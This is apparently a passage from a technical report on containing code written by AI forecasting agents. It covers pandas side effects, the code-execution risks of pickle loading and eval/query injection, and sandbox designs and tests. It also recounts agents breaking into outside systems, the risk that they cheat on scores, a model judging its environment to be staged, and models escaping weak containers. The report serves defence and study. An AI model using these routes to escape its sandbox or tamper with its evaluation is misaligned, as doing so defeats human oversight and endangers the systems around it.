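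The agents in the three July investigations were taking cybersecurity tests that required them to break into something, often with the usual filters off. A forecasting agent has no such task, and a developer who uses a released model normally gets its safeguards. OpenAI's *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* claims that the guardrails in the company's products would have detected the incident as unsafe, and Anthropic makes a similar claim about its own safeguards. These are the companies' own assessments, and they concern cyberattacks. A filter against cyber misuse would probably miss a program that opens a file of outcomes with pandas, because it resembles ordinary data analysis.

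The pressure to cheat is probably weaker in forecasting too. An agent given a security task with no solution fails unless it cheats. A forecaster can always submit an honest probability, and even on a question that nobody can predict, a forecast of 50% gets a Brier score of only 0.25. But an agent that seeks the lowest possible score can still gain by cheating, because honest forecasts of uncertain events rarely score zero.

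Forecasting agents can use some of the same models and have the same kind of access as the agents in these cases. GPT-5.6 Sol, which had the best score in *Forecast-Dojo*, was also among the models in OpenAI's July experiments and in AISI's runs. AISI's agents needed only an open connection, which many live forecasting agents have for research. Anthropic's case also shows that a prompt instruction such as "use only articles from before March 1" doesn't block access and is no substitute for a restriction that does.

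Back-tests add another risk, because the evaluator may tell the agent that today is a date in the past. Mythos 5 treated the year 2026 on the systems it reached as proof that they were staged, although the year was correct. An agent that notices a false date has better reason to conclude that nothing around it is real, and it may then take less care with real systems it can reach.

No public report appears to document a forecasting agent stealing a key, attacking a system or tampering with its own score. Researchers describe more ordinary failures. Agents in *FutureSim* had shell and file tools inside a sandbox, and Goel and colleagues report overconfidence, too few updates and too much trust in earlier notes. GPT-5.5 gave 27.4% of its wrong final answers a probability of at least 50%. *Temporal Leakage in Search-Engine Date-Filtered Web Retrieval* (2026) traces inflated scores to search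 engines returning pages that had changed after the cutoff. The survey *LLM-based Agents for Forecasting and Prediction* (2026) attributes leakage to data and training, and its discussion of the sources of leakage does not mention deliberate cheating.

This absence is only weak evidence of good behaviour. An agent in a sandbox has few opportunities to misbehave, and misconduct can go unnoticed until someone reads the logs. Anthropic's earliest incident happened in April, but the company didn't find it until late July, after OpenAI's disclosure prompted it to review its own tests. The two affected organisations that Anthropic reached had not detected the intrusions either.

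## Which library calls do more than compute?

A common precaution is to let the agent import only familiar libraries, such as pandas and NumPy. This keeps out packages from unknown authors, but it doesn't limit the agent to calculation. pandas can also move data between files, databases and web servers, and a few of its functions can execute code contained in a file or a string.

The following program imports nothing but pandas. Suppose `source` holds a location that the agent took from an article:

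```python
import pandas as pd
df = pd.read_csv(source)
north = df[df["region"] == "North"]
north.to_csv("elections.csv", index=False)
print(north["incumbent_lost"].mean())
```

The third and fifth lines only compute. The second reads a local file if `source` is a file name, or contacts a server if `source` is a web address. The fourth writes a file, and by default `to_csv` replaces any existing file of that name. One such line can cause the earlier mistake of overwriting a full election dataset with one region's results.

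The name of a function is therefore not enough to classify it. For example, `to_json` returns a string if the program gives it no file path and writes a file if the program does. The table sorts common calls by what they can do:

| Operation | Typical calls | Effect beyond computing | Safer alternative |
|---|---|---|---|
| Filtering, averaging, simulating | `groupby`, `merge`, NumPy's `percentile` | Uses memory and time | The same calls, with limits on both |
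| Reading a local file | `read_csv`, `read_parquet` | Can open any file the process may read | One folder of supplied data |
| Writing a file | `to_csv`, `to_parquet` | Can replace existing data | A new file in a temporary folder |
| Reading from a web address | `read_csv`, `read_json` | Contacts a server and can send it data | A copy that the harness has downloaded |
| Using a database | `read_sql`, `to_sql` | Can change or delete records | An account that can only read |
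| Loading a pickle | `read_pickle` | Can execute code | Parquet, CSV or JSON |
| Evaluating an expression | `eval`, `query` | Can execute code | An ordinary filter, as in the third line above |
| Downloading market data | yfinance's `download` | Contacts the data provider | A saved price series with its retrieval date |
| Installing a package | `pip install` | Downloads code and may run it | Libraries installed in advance at fixed versions |

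### Web addresses, files and databases

The pandas guide to reading and writing data, *IO tools (text, CSV, HDF5, …)*, includes an example that downloads a table from the US Bureau of Labor Statistics with a single `read_csv` call. An agent forecasting next month's inflation could easily write the same line, and a checker that looks for imports of networking libraries would not flag it.

Many of pandas's reading and writing functions accept remote locations. For anything other than local files and ordinary web addresses, pandas uses the fsspec package, if it is installed. With the right additional packages, fsspec can reach Amazon S3, Google Cloud, and machines that accept SSH or FTP connections. These packages can take credentials from environment variables or configuration files, so a program can open a company's private storage even if its source code contains no password.

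A program can also send data out while it reads. Every web request includes an address, and pandas lets a program add its own headers, which are extra lines of text sent with the request. Either can carry information from the host to the server's owner, so letting an agent read the web but not post to it does little to protect secrets on the host. Reading can also write to the local disk, because fsspec has an option that keeps a temporary or permanent copy of each downloaded file.

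Packages for market data do more than compute. For example, yfinance downloads share prices from Yahoo Finance, so an allow-list that includes it permits network access. In a back-test, such a package can also return prices from after the cutoff. If the harness downloads the prices and passes them to the agent in a file, the program can do the same calculations without a connection. The developer also keeps a record of the exact data used for each forecast.

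The names of database functions are especially misleading. `read_sql` takes a statement in SQL, the standard database language, and returns the result as a table. According to the pandas developers, the library passes the statement to the database driver without trying to sanitise it. A call to `read_sql` can therefore delete every record if the driver and the account permit it. Chhabra and colleagues describe prompt-to-SQL attacks, in which an attacker's text leads a model to write database commands that the developer wanted to forbid. A read-only database account prevents such a deletion whatever the model writes.

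Even a query that only reads data can affect other users, because a program that leaves its connection open may lock the database. The writing function, `to_sql`, is safer than `to_csv` in one respect, because by default it raises an error if the table already exists.

### Why loading a pickle can run code

Pickle is Python's format for saving objects, and developers often use it for tables and fitted models. Unlike a CSV file, which contains only text, a pickle contains instructions for rebuilding objects, and these can include calls to Python functions. Whoever made the file chooses the functions, and they run during loading, before the agent's program can check the loaded data.

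The pandas developers warn that loading pickled data from untrusted sources with `read_pickle` can be unsafe. The function also accepts a web address, so one call can download a stranger's file and run the code inside it. A forecasting agent might do this innocently after finding a dataset or ready-made model shared as a pickle.

In July 2022 a software engineer wrote to the pandas developers because a security scan had flagged `read_pickle` in every version of the library. Augspurger (2022) replied in *Security Issue* that the function works as intended, that the documentation describes the risk, and that the developers had disputed the report. This is reasonable, since pickle could not restore arbitrary Python objects without calling functions, but it also means that no future update will make the function safe for files from strangers. NumPy's developers chose a more cautious default for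 `load`, which rejects pickled objects unless the program explicitly allows them.

Tables rarely need to be saved with pickle. Parquet, a compact file format, preserves dates and column types, and pandas raises an error if a program tries to store arbitrary Python objects in it. CSV and JSON files can be read in any text editor, but some values can change when pandas reads them back. For example, code 036 in the CAMEO system for classifying international events means an intention to meet or negotiate. If an agent saves a column of CAMEO codes as CSV and reads it back with default settings, 036 becomes the number 36. A search for "036" then finds nothing, and the agent may conclude that two governments have never expressed an intention to meet. When reading JSON, pandas may turn large whole numbers into dates if the column has a name such as `modified` or one ending in `_at`.

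A program can prevent both errors by stating the column types when it reads the file. The errors are worse than pickle in one practical sense, because they happen by default to honest users, but they damage one analysis and can't give a stranger control of the process. Pickle files may also become unreadable over time, because the developers guarantee `read_pickle` only for files from the current or previous major version of pandas.

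### Expressions in strings

Some pandas functions accept a small expression as text. For example, an agent can keep recent elections with `df.query("year >= 2000")` instead of the ordinary filter `df[df["year"] >= 2000]`. The pandas developers warn that two related functions, `pandas.eval` and `DataFrame.eval`, can run arbitrary code if a program passes user input to them.

This warning matters a great deal to a developer who has decided against a code tool and built something narrower, though it matters little if the agent can already write any Python program. Suppose the model may only supply a filter, which the harness passes to `query` inside its own process. The filter can contain code that runs with all the harness's permissions, even though the developer may believe the model can only select rows. A model might write such a filter after reading an injected instruction.

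According to the security company Snyk, people have found public web services with this weakness. Snyk doesn't class it as a vulnerability in pandas, because the developers never promised that `query` was safe for untrusted text. The developers have added a warning to the documentation. The reported weakness has a CVE number (an identifier for a publicly reported vulnerability), CVE-2024-9880, but VulDB's *pandas up to 2.2.2 pandas.DataFrame.query code injection* (2025) marks it as a false positive. An agent's use of pandas may therefore be unsafe even if a scan finds no known vulnerabilities in the library.

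Developers can make a narrow filter tool safe by giving the model separate fields for the column, the comparison and the value. The harness checks the column and comparison against short lists of allowed options and treats the value only as data. This allows fewer kinds of filter, but the model no longer supplies anything that Python executes.

### A chart tool that ran any program

Developers of data-analysis tools have made a similar mistake with whole programs. Chhabra and colleagues cite CVE-2024-5565 as a real case in which code written by a model led to arbitrary code execution. The vulnerability was in Vanna, a Python library that lets people query a database in ordinary language. The model writes an SQL query and can then write a short Python program to chart the results. Vanna ran this program with `exec` in its own process.

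Vanna's developer expected chart code, but nothing restricted the program to drawing charts. Someone could phrase a question so that the model wrote other code, which then ran with the application's permissions. The developer responded with a guide that advises users to run the chart function in a sandbox. This is sensible because a better prompt or a longer list of forbidden words would have left the program with the same permissions.

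The same reasoning applies to a forecasting harness whose code tool is described as "for calculating base rates". The description may influence what code the model writes, but the interpreter runs any code it receives.

### Restrictions inside Python

Developers who want firmer rules than a description provides often try to enforce them within Python, in three main ways. An import allow-list blocks every library except those named. A source check parses the program into a syntax tree, a structured form of the code, and rejects certain calls before anything runs. The harness can also run the program without certain built-in functions, such as `open`.

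An allow-list restricts only the program's own imports, so an allowed library can still do things that the program could not do directly. For example, pandas must import many other modules to do its work, including those for files and network connections. Programs can often reach these modules through pandas too.

The harness removes `open` from the agent's program, but pandas functions keep their own access to it, so the program can still read a file with `read_csv` and overwrite one with `to_csv`. Removing `open` from pandas as well would stop the library from reading the data that the agent needs.

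A source check examines only the text of a program, before the program's variables have values. In the example at the start of this section, the text `read_csv(source)` doesn't show whether `source` is a file or a web address. The check could require every location to appear as plain text in the call, but this would also reject a harmless loop over 12 monthly files. Python can also look up a function by name while a program is running, so a forbidden call may not appear in the source in a recognisable form.

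Repairing these gaps one at a time is difficult because Python lets programs inspect and modify most of their own parts, and an attacker needs only one route that the developer missed. In many designs, the restricted program also runs in the same process as the harness, so a single gap exposes the harness's memory and API keys.

The maintainers of such tools make no strong claims about their security. The documentation of RestrictedPython, a package that allows only a limited version of Python, states that it is not a sandbox. Hugging Face's agent library smolagents has a local executor that checks imports and interprets the model's program one operation at a time. Its maintainers warn developers not to rely on it as a security boundary and recommend isolated environments for untrusted code. LangChain, another agent library, has an experimental agent for pandas tables that will not start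 unless the developer sets the option `allow_dangerous_code`.

These restrictions are still useful against mistakes. Fluid Attacks' *Python Untrusted Pickle File Deserialization*, a rule for checking source code, flags calls to `read_pickle` where an outsider could control the file. It would catch an agent that carelessly loaded a pickle from a website, because the agent would have no reason to disguise the call. The harness could return the message "pickle files are not allowed, look for a CSV or Parquet version", and the model could correct its program in the next round.

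A check of this kind takes almost no compute and leaves a record of what the agent tried. Its main drawback is false alarms. If it blocks every use of `query`, an agent will sometimes waste one of its limited rounds rewriting a harmless filter. A developer can reduce this waste by listing the rules in the tool's description. For anything that must not happen even once, such as a trade above a set size, the restriction has to be outside the Python process.

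### Fixed library versions

Any list of allowed or forbidden functions depends on the version of the library. Developers can pin each library to an exact version, which stays installed until they decide to change it. In GlucoAgent, Sun and colleagues pin Python 3.9.25, along with NumPy 1.26.4, SciPy 1.13.0, pandas 2.2.2, scikit-learn 1.4.2 and statsmodels 0.14.2. Every forecast in their test therefore used the same functions with the same defaults.

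Upgrading a library can undo a restriction even if nobody edits the rules. Version 3.0 of pandas added functions for reading and writing Iceberg tables, a format for very large datasets that often sit in remote storage. A list of forbidden functions written for version 2.2.2 would not contain `read_iceberg`, so the checker would allow it after the upgrade. With a list of permitted functions, the checker would block `read_iceberg` until someone added it, so an allow-list is the better choice here.

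Upgrades can also change results. In pandas 3, text columns have the type `str` by default, where earlier versions used `object`. A model that learnt from older examples may write code that identifies text columns by the old type and therefore skips them. If a developer upgrades halfway through a comparison of two agents, part of the difference in their scores may come from the library.

Pinning also protects against a malicious new release of a genuine package, at least until the next upgrade. It works fully only if the developer also pins the packages that pandas depends on and checks each download against a recorded hash, a short code computed from the file's contents. However, pinned versions don't receive security fixes automatically, and old versions eventually stop getting them at all, as Python 3.9 did in October 2025. Repeatable results are worth that drawback for a benchmark that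 runs offline in a sandbox, but a live agent with network access needs a schedule for upgrading and retesting.

### Permission in the prompt or limits in the environment

The forecasting benchmark MIRAI and the glucose forecaster GlucoAgent have nearly opposite policies on libraries. MIRAI tests forecasts of how one country will act towards another, such as whether Australia will criticise China on a given day. Agents query a database of past events and news through a set of Python functions. In the version that lets agents write whole programs, *MIRAI* (Ye, Hu and colleagues, 2024) also authorises the model to use "safe, well-established Python libraries such as numpy, pandas, scikit-learn, and NetworkX". (This is Chenchen Ye, not the Liqin Ye of *Forecast-Dojo*.)

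This rule is an instruction in a prompt, so it can't block an import. The words "such as" leave the list open, so the model has to decide whether an unlisted library is safe. The rule also doesn't distinguish between functions within a listed library. `read_pickle` belongs to a well-established library, so a model could follow the rule exactly and still execute code from a downloaded file. MIRAI describes running its programs in a Python code sandbox with full access to the database, so the prompt need not be the only protection. On its own, though, the rule works only if the model knows which calls have side effects and keeps following the rule after reading hostile text.

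GlucoAgent's prompt contains almost no rules about libraries. Sun and colleagues tell the model that "normal imports work" and that it may use `pathlib`, a standard module for handling files, which a strict import list would probably refuse. They restrict the environment instead. The interpreter has no network connection, the patient's data file is read-only, and the environment variables contain no credentials. The same few programs have very different effects under the two approaches:

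| What the program does | With only a rule in the prompt | In GlucoAgent's environment |
|---|---|---|
| Reads a CSV file from a web address | Works if the host is online | Fails |
| Overwrites the supplied data | Works if the process may write there | Fails |
| Saves an intermediate table | May replace something important | Works in a private folder that disappears after the forecast |
| Installs another package | Works if the host is online | Fails |
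| Loads a pickle | Can run code with the host's permissions | Can run code only within the same limits |

GlucoAgent's policy doesn't require the model to recognise a dangerous call. It relies on the developer to configure the environment correctly and supply all the data the forecast needs. Supplying all the data is easy when it consists of a patient's glucose records, but much harder when the agent has to research the news. Some instructions still depend on the model's compliance, such as Sun and colleagues' instruction never to invent missing facts, which no sandbox can enforce.

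A third policy is to offer a fixed menu of operations and no general Python. In one version of MIRAI, each action must be a single call to one of the benchmark's own functions, so the model has no occasion to use pickle, write a file or download a table. In a test with the same underlying model, agents limited to single calls scored 29.6 on F1, against 12.6 for agents that wrote programs. F1 runs from 0 to 100, rewarding correct event types and penalising wrong guesses. Many of the programs failed. About half the runs of the small model Mistral-7B ended after repeated invalid actions when it had to write programs, compared with about a quarter when it made single calls. Ye and colleagues found that only GPT-4o benefited from writing programs.

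Those models are now more than two years old, and GlucoAgent's result suggests the opposite. Sun and colleagues first built a version without Python that had six tools for retrieving readings, events and summary statistics. On the same test cases and with the same model, the version with Python had an average error 1.71 mg/dL lower. It beat Chronos-2 by about 1 mg/dL, so the version without Python would have had a larger error than Chronos-2.

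The two versions also differed in their prompts and call limits, although the version with six tools never reached its limit. Sun and colleagues note that they tried only one such menu and that a better one might do as well as Python. A strong model probably loses some accuracy when it can't write its own analysis, at least on large tables of numbers. On questions that depend mainly on news, where Python seems to add little, a developer could replace it with a few fixed calculations, such as a base rate or a running total, and probably lose very little accuracy.

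## How does a sandbox contain the code?

A firm restriction has to be enforced outside the Python process, and most sandboxes enforce it at the kernel, the core of the operating system. A program can add numbers on its own, but it needs the kernel to open a file, contact a server or start another program. Each request to the kernel is a system call. Python's `open` and pandas's `read_csv` make the same system call to open a local file, so a kernel rule covers both, along with any library the developer forgot to list.

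The table lists the mechanisms roughly from weakest to strongest. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) gives approximate start-up times for most of them, and the figure in the last row comes from *WebAssembly and Unikernels* (2025).

| Mechanism | What it adds | What the operator still has to trust | Start-up |
|---|---|---|---|
| Process with limits | Caps on time, memory and file size | The program itself | Python's own |
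| Namespaces (bubblewrap, firejail) | A private view of files, network and processes | The whole host kernel | 30 ms |
| Container (rootless Docker) | Packaged libraries and a system-call filter | The host kernel, apart from the filtered calls | 300 ms |
| User-space kernel (gVisor) | A second kernel that handles most system calls | gVisor and the part of the host kernel it uses | 200 ms |
| Small virtual machine (Firecracker) | A separate kernel on virtual hardware | The virtual-machine software and the processor | 100 ms |
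| WebAssembly (Wasmtime) | Access only to functions the host supplies | The WebAssembly runtime | 6 ms |

Stronger isolation does not always start more slowly. Docker takes longest in these figures, although it offers less protection than gVisor or Firecracker.

### Limits on an ordinary process

The simplest sandbox runs the code in a second interpreter, and the kernel caps its memory, processor time and file sizes. The harness also kills the process after a set time. These limits stop an endless loop or an oversized array but don't restrict the program's access to files or the network. Wang and Zheng fairly describe such controls as weak.

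If the harness runs the code with Python's `subprocess.run`, a time-out kills the program but not any processes the program has started. These can keep running while the harness moves on to the next question.

### Namespaces and system-call filters

A Linux namespace gives a process its own version of one part of the system. With a new mount namespace, the harness can control which files and folders the code can access. A new network namespace has no connection to the outside until someone adds one. A new process namespace hides the host's other processes. When the first process in it ends, the kernel kills all the others inside, so a timer that kills the first process also stops the rest. Tools such as bubblewrap and firejail set up these namespaces without a full container.

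The program still makes its system calls to the host's kernel, and a bug in any of several hundred calls might let it escape the sandbox. A seccomp filter reduces this risk by blocking calls the program doesn't need. The filter can check a call's number and simple arguments, which is enough to block new network connections. It can't read the text of a file path, so it can't allow access to a dataset while blocking access to a password file. Landlock, a newer kernel feature, can restrict access by path.

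Wang and Zheng's tool, Sandlock, combines Landlock with seccomp and needs no administrator rights. In their own evaluation, which they call preliminary, it started a command in about 6 ms and showed no slowdown in a database test. Sandlock can also hold back a program's changes to files until the harness accepts or discards them. A harness could use this to undo a mistake such as the overwritten election dataset.

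### Containers

Docker and similar systems combine namespaces and a system-call filter with an image, a packaged file system that holds Python and its libraries. They can also use control groups to cap memory, processor use and the number of processes for a whole container. The same image runs on a laptop and in a data centre, which makes experiments easier to repeat.

Containers use little memory. *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs* (2026) describes a system that gives a language model a container for general tasks. All tasks share one image of about 1.1 GB, and each container uses about 50 MB of memory when idle and 200 MB at its peak. Running 512 of them at once takes about 100 GB, or 5% of the memory on the paper's server.

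The main weakness of containers is the kernel they share with the host, along with the software that starts them. Rashidi cites a 2024 flaw in runc, the program that starts containers in Docker and many other systems. The program left open a reference to a folder on the host, which a specially prepared container could use to reach the host's file system. The developers have fixed this flaw, but any container-based sandbox remains exposed to new flaws of the same kind.

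Poor configuration is probably a more common problem. In *SandboxEval*, Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues (2025) cite an industry survey in which 76% of Docker containers ran with elevated privileges. They also report seeing some researchers run model-written code directly on a laptop with few or no protections.

### A second kernel

gVisor runs between the container and the host's kernel. It carries out most Linux system calls in its own code and passes a much smaller set of requests to the host. To exploit a bug in the host's handling of some obscure call, a program would usually have to break gVisor first.

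OpenAI used gVisor when testing Codex, an early model for writing code. According to *Evaluating Large Language Models Trained on Code* (2021), the team chose it because ordinary containers can share the host's resources, so a malicious container could compromise the host. They also added firewall rules that blocked every connection the experiment didn't need. gVisor protects the host's kernel but doesn't restrict which servers a program may contact.

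This kind of sandbox slows system calls, and some software does not run in it at all. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (Podala Narasimha, 2026) notes that the slowdown affects programs that make many such calls. A NumPy simulation makes few of them once it is running, so most of the delay for a forecasting agent should come at the start, when Python opens many library files.

Firecracker and Kata Containers give each sandbox its own complete kernel on virtual hardware. A program that exploits a bug in that kernel controls only its virtual machine. To reach the host, it must also exploit a flaw in the software that runs the virtual machine or in the processor. The host must support hardware virtualisation, which some rented servers don't offer.

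In *WebAssembly and Unikernels*, Firecracker took 94.1 ms to start from nothing, close to Wang and Zheng's estimate, and 30.1 ms with the virtual network adapter and other parts prepared in advance. The guests in this test were unikernels, programs packaged with only the parts of an operating system they need. A guest that boots ordinary Linux and then loads pandas will probably take longer.

### WebAssembly

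WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that browser makers designed for running compiled programs in web pages. A WebAssembly program has its own block of memory and can call only the functions its host supplies. If the host supplies no function for opening files, the program cannot open one.

Wasmtime, which runs such programs outside the browser, started an empty function in 5.6 ms in the same comparison, but its start-up time depended more on the complexity of the code than Firecracker's did. Firecracker ran both test applications faster, computing a fractal in 151 ms and processing an image in 101 ms.

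Library support is a bigger obstacle for forecasting. Packages that contain compiled code, such as NumPy and pandas, will not load until someone rebuilds them for WebAssembly. The Pyodide project has done this for NumPy, pandas and SciPy. Pure Python packages do not need rebuilding. Pyodide also lets Python call JavaScript, so the operator has to restrict the JavaScript environment too.

WebAssembly's place at the strong end of the table is debatable. A WebAssembly program can't make system calls directly, but its runtime is usually an ordinary process with the full permissions of the user running it. A bug in the runtime could give the program those permissions, so a cautious operator would put the runtime inside one of the other sandboxes.

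### How much start-up time matters

For an agent making one forecast, start-up time matters little. Sun and colleagues report that a typical GlucoAgent forecast ran about seven programs and took 174 seconds. Even at Docker's 300 ms per program, start-up would account for 2.1 seconds, or 1.2% of the total. In *Computer Environments Elicit General Agentic Intelligence in LLMs*, running code took 2.3% of the total time for a DeepSeek model.

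Docker's start-up time matters more during training. *ALPHABET* (Ye et al.) collects 2,048 forecasting attempts before each round of training when the agent keeps no notes between dates. If each attempt ran ten programs, starting Docker would take about 1.7 hours of machine time per round, though many machines can share that work.

Loading packages and data into a sandbox often takes longer than creating its boundary. A single image with everything in it is slow to load, and a small one lacks packages that some programs need. *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026) avoids this choice by preparing a set of small snapshots, which are saved states with different packages already loaded. The set, planned using 15,000 scripts, made start-up 3 to 22 times faster and whole runs 1.3 to 3.3 times faster than existing approaches with the same storage. Forecasting programs mostly import the same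 few libraries, so one snapshot might be enough for them.

Sandboxes started from the same snapshot can produce the same random numbers. NumPy seeds its older, global random-number generator when a program imports the library. If the snapshot was taken after the import, every copy will draw the same numbers from that generator unless the program sets a new seed. An agent that ran the same simulation in five copies without reseeding would get five identical answers and might mistake them for independent results that agree.

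### GlucoAgent's sandbox, setting by setting

Sun and colleagues create a new sandbox for every glucose forecast and destroy it afterwards. Each program the agent writes gets a new interpreter in a bubblewrap container. A command built from the settings they list would look roughly like this:

```bash
timeout -s KILL 8 \
prlimit --cpu=8 --as=536870912 --fsize=1048576 --nofile=64 --core=0 \
bwrap --unshare-all --die-with-parent --clearenv \
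  --setenv PATH /usr/bin --setenv PYTHONHASHSEED 0 --setenv OMP_NUM_THREADS 1 \
  --ro-bind /usr /usr --symlink usr/lib /lib --symlink usr/lib64 /lib64 \
  --ro-bind /opt/py39 /opt/py39 --proc /proc --dev /dev --tmpfs /tmp \
  --ro-bind case.json /input/case.json --bind scratch /work --chdir /work \
  /opt/py39/bin/python program.py
```

The first two lines limit time and resources. `--unshare-all` creates the new namespaces, including an empty network. `--ro-bind` makes a file or folder visible but read-only, and `--bind` also allows writing. The host's other files do not exist inside the sandbox, so the program cannot reach the harness's source code, the true glucose values or the records for other forecasts.

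| Setting | Failure it prevents | Failure it leaves |
|---|---|---|
| Empty network namespace | Downloading files, installing packages, sending data out | Private data in printed output still reaches the model's provider |
| One read-only data file | Changing the patient's records | Errors already in the file |
| Private `/work` folder | Overwriting another forecast's files | Reusing a damaged table later in the same forecast |
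| Cleared environment variables | Printing an API key | Reading a key from a file that the developer mounts by mistake |
| 8 seconds of elapsed time | Waiting or looping forever | Overloading the machine for 8 seconds |
| 8 seconds of processor time | Using many cores for the whole period | Starting more processes, each with its own allowance |
| 512 MiB of address space | Creating one enormous array | Using more memory through several processes |
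| 1 MiB per file | Writing one enormous file | Filling the disk with small files |
| 64 open files | Using up the host's supply of file handles | Opening more files through several processes |

The sandbox also disables core dumps, the files in which Linux can save a crashed program's memory. Otherwise a crash could leave a patient's data on the disk.

Sun and colleagues limit address space, the range of memory addresses a program has reserved, whether or not it uses them. Under a 512 MiB limit, a program can hold at most 67 million eight-byte numbers, and fewer in practice because Python and its libraries also need space. The 8-gigabyte array from the earlier example fails immediately with a `MemoryError`. The model can read the error and rewrite the simulation to keep only the current step.

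The single-thread setting helps numerical libraries stay within these limits. These libraries often start one thread per processor core, and every thread reserves address space. On a machine with eight cores, the threads could also use up the eight seconds of processor time in one second. The fixed hash seed makes Python order sets of strings the same way on every run, which helps others reproduce a result, but it does not fix NumPy's random numbers.

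Sun and colleagues list no cap on the number of processes or on total disk space. Linux normally applies the address-space limit to each process separately, so 20 processes could together reserve 10 GiB. A program that kept starting copies of itself could slow the machine for eight seconds, which could delay other forecasts because the harness processes many at the same time. On a disk that writes 500 MB a second, one program could produce about 4 GB of small files, and an agent may run 14 programs per forecast. Destroying the sandbox removes these files, but the disk could fill up first.

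Control groups and a disk quota would close both gaps. Podala Narasimha specifies a hardened sandbox for Kubernetes, a system for managing containers across many machines. The sandbox limits the whole container to one processor, 1 GiB of memory and 512 MiB of temporary storage. Wang and Zheng do not use control groups in Sandlock. They consider their own limits sufficient for accidents but recommend control groups against programs that deliberately try to exhaust memory.

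The sandboxed program still shares the host's kernel, and bubblewrap filters system calls only if the developer supplies a filter. Sun and colleagues mention none, so a program that exploited an unpatched kernel bug could escape every restriction in the table. This risk seems acceptable for GlucoAgent, which reads records from a public research dataset and never opens a web page, so an outsider has almost no way to supply it with malicious code. Developers have more reason to run an agent's programs under gVisor or in a virtual machine if the agent reads the open web.

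### AlphaBet and Forecast-Dojo

*ALPHABET* gives each Python call a fresh sandbox with no network and no access to the local file system. The file restriction presumably covers only the host's files, since Python has to load its libraries from somewhere. Each call can run for up to 10 seconds and use up to 4 GiB of memory. Ye and colleagues don't name the isolation mechanism in their description of the tool, so it is unclear whether programs share the host's kernel.

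*Forecast-Dojo* gives less detail. Ye and colleagues say the code runs in a sandbox, but their instructions to the model mention the ten-second limit without mentioning any limits on network access, files or memory. *ALPHABET* uses the same environment, so the two projects may share a sandbox, but a team that wants to repeat the benchmark safely would have to check this in the code.

AlphaBet's memory limit is eight times GlucoAgent's. A simulation that stores 100,000 price paths of 1,000 steps each needs 800 MB, so it would run in AlphaBet's sandbox but fail in GlucoAgent's. If the program keeps only the current price on each path, it needs less than 1 MB. A low limit therefore rules out few forecasting calculations, but the agent may need an extra call to rewrite a program that stores too much data.

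A generous limit can require a lot of memory when many agents run at once. If all 2,048 attempts in a training round used their full 4 GiB at the same moment, they would need 8 TiB. Most programs use far less, so operators usually provide enough memory for typical use and accept that a few programs will fail when it runs short.

### Fresh and persistent interpreters

A persistent interpreter keeps its variables between calls, as a notebook does, so the agent can load a large table once and work on it in several steps. With a fresh interpreter for each call, the agent has to reload the table every time, but the code raises an error if the agent forgets to define something it needs.

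Suppose an agent uses the flood formula from the start, with 6 floods in 40 years, to answer a question about the next three months. It then moves on to a question about the next six months but doesn't set the new value of `t`. A fresh interpreter stops with a `NameError`, while a persistent one still has `t = 0.25` and prints 3.7% instead of 7.2%.

GlucoAgent runs every program in a fresh interpreter but keeps files in `/work` until the end of the forecast, so the agent can save a cleaned table and reload it without depending on old variables. However, if a program saves a file as `pandas.py`, a later script in the same folder will load that file when it imports pandas, because Python searches the script's own folder before the installed libraries. A model could do this by accident or because of an injected instruction. Sun and colleagues delete the folder after each forecast, so the problem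 can't carry over to the next one.

State that passes between questions is harder to justify. Podala Narasimha warns that a sandbox shared by successive users can contaminate later sessions. If it holds medical data, it could also expose one patient's records during another patient's forecast. In a back-test, an agent might save a table while forecasting an event in May and then find it while forecasting an earlier one in March. Scores would also depend on the order of the questions, so an evaluator couldn't reproduce a single forecast without rerunning everything before it.

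Some information has to carry over when an agent revisits the same event. *Forecast-Dojo* and *ALPHABET* provide an optional notebook for this, where the model records its probabilities, evidence and open questions. At the next date, the agent gets the notebook and a new conversation, but no variables or files from its earlier programs. The evaluator can read the whole notebook, whereas memory left in an interpreter is much harder to inspect. *FutureSim*, whose agents keep files over many simulated days, also needs date controls on the sandbox.

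If creating a new sandbox for each question takes too long, the harness can reset a used one to a clean state. Rashidi describes a system called DeltaBox that saves only the changes between one state and the next, and can roll a sandbox back in less than ten milliseconds.

### What sandbox tests have found

The ranking of mechanisms from process limits to virtual machines is based mostly on reasoning about their design. Rashidi found that researchers almost never compare isolation systems on a shared benchmark, so there are no comparable escape rates. Existing tests cover narrower questions.

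SandboxEval checks whether a particular sandbox does what its operator intended. Rabin and colleagues wrote its 51 Python tests, each of which attempts something a sandbox may need to block. Nineteen look for information, such as environment variables and folder contents. Another 17 try to read or change files and their permissions, eight try to communicate outside the sandbox, and seven attempt dangerous operations such as filling the disk or shutting down the machine.

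The team ran the tests on one installation of Dyff, an open-source framework for evaluating AI models. The results mostly confirmed that the restrictions worked. However, programs could read environment variables that needed further investigation, so the team reviewed the configuration. The finding is modest, but developers often keep API keys in environment variables.

Some of the 51 tests in SandboxEval attempt things that programs often have a legitimate need to do, such as checking the time zone or listing their working folder. A sandbox that allows these attempts is not necessarily faulty, so the number of blocked attempts is a poor measure of safety. Operators have to decide in advance which attempts should fail.

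SandboxEscapeBench, which Rashidi also reviews, instead tests whether models can escape from containers deliberately built with known weaknesses, including configuration mistakes, excessive privileges and kernel flaws. Capable models found and exploited these weaknesses, which is a good reason to patch and configure containers carefully. The results don't show how often a model would escape from a container without a known weakness.

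Filters that block specific shell commands can often be bypassed. The ShellSieve system tested 1,709 lists of forbidden commands from public code on GitHub. It used a language model to propose bypasses and a sandbox to check whether they worked. Between 69.0% and 98.6% of the lists were vulnerable, depending on the type of bypass. A harness that lets its agent run shell commands should therefore rely on restrictions on files and network access, which apply whatever command the agent runs.

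### How to check that the limits hold

An operator can test a sandbox in the same way as Rabin and colleagues, with a few small programs sent through the agent's own code tool. Testing the container by hand is less reliable, because the harness may start it with different settings. For a sandbox like GlucoAgent's, with the missing caps added, the tests could be these:

| Test program | Expected result |
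|---|---|
| Contacts the operator's own server, by name and by numerical address | Both attempts fail and the server logs nothing |
| Searches for a fake key that the operator has put in the harness's environment and home folder | It finds nothing |
| Tries to overwrite the data file | An error, and the file on the host is unchanged |
| Creates a 600 MiB array | `MemoryError` |
| Writes a 2 MiB file | "File too large" |
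| Starts a second process and then loops forever | Both processes have disappeared from the host after eight seconds |
| Starts 200 processes | The kernel refuses most of them |
| Writes 1 MiB files until it fails | It reaches the quota and the host's disk still has space |
| Saves a file, then looks for it during the next forecast | The file is missing |

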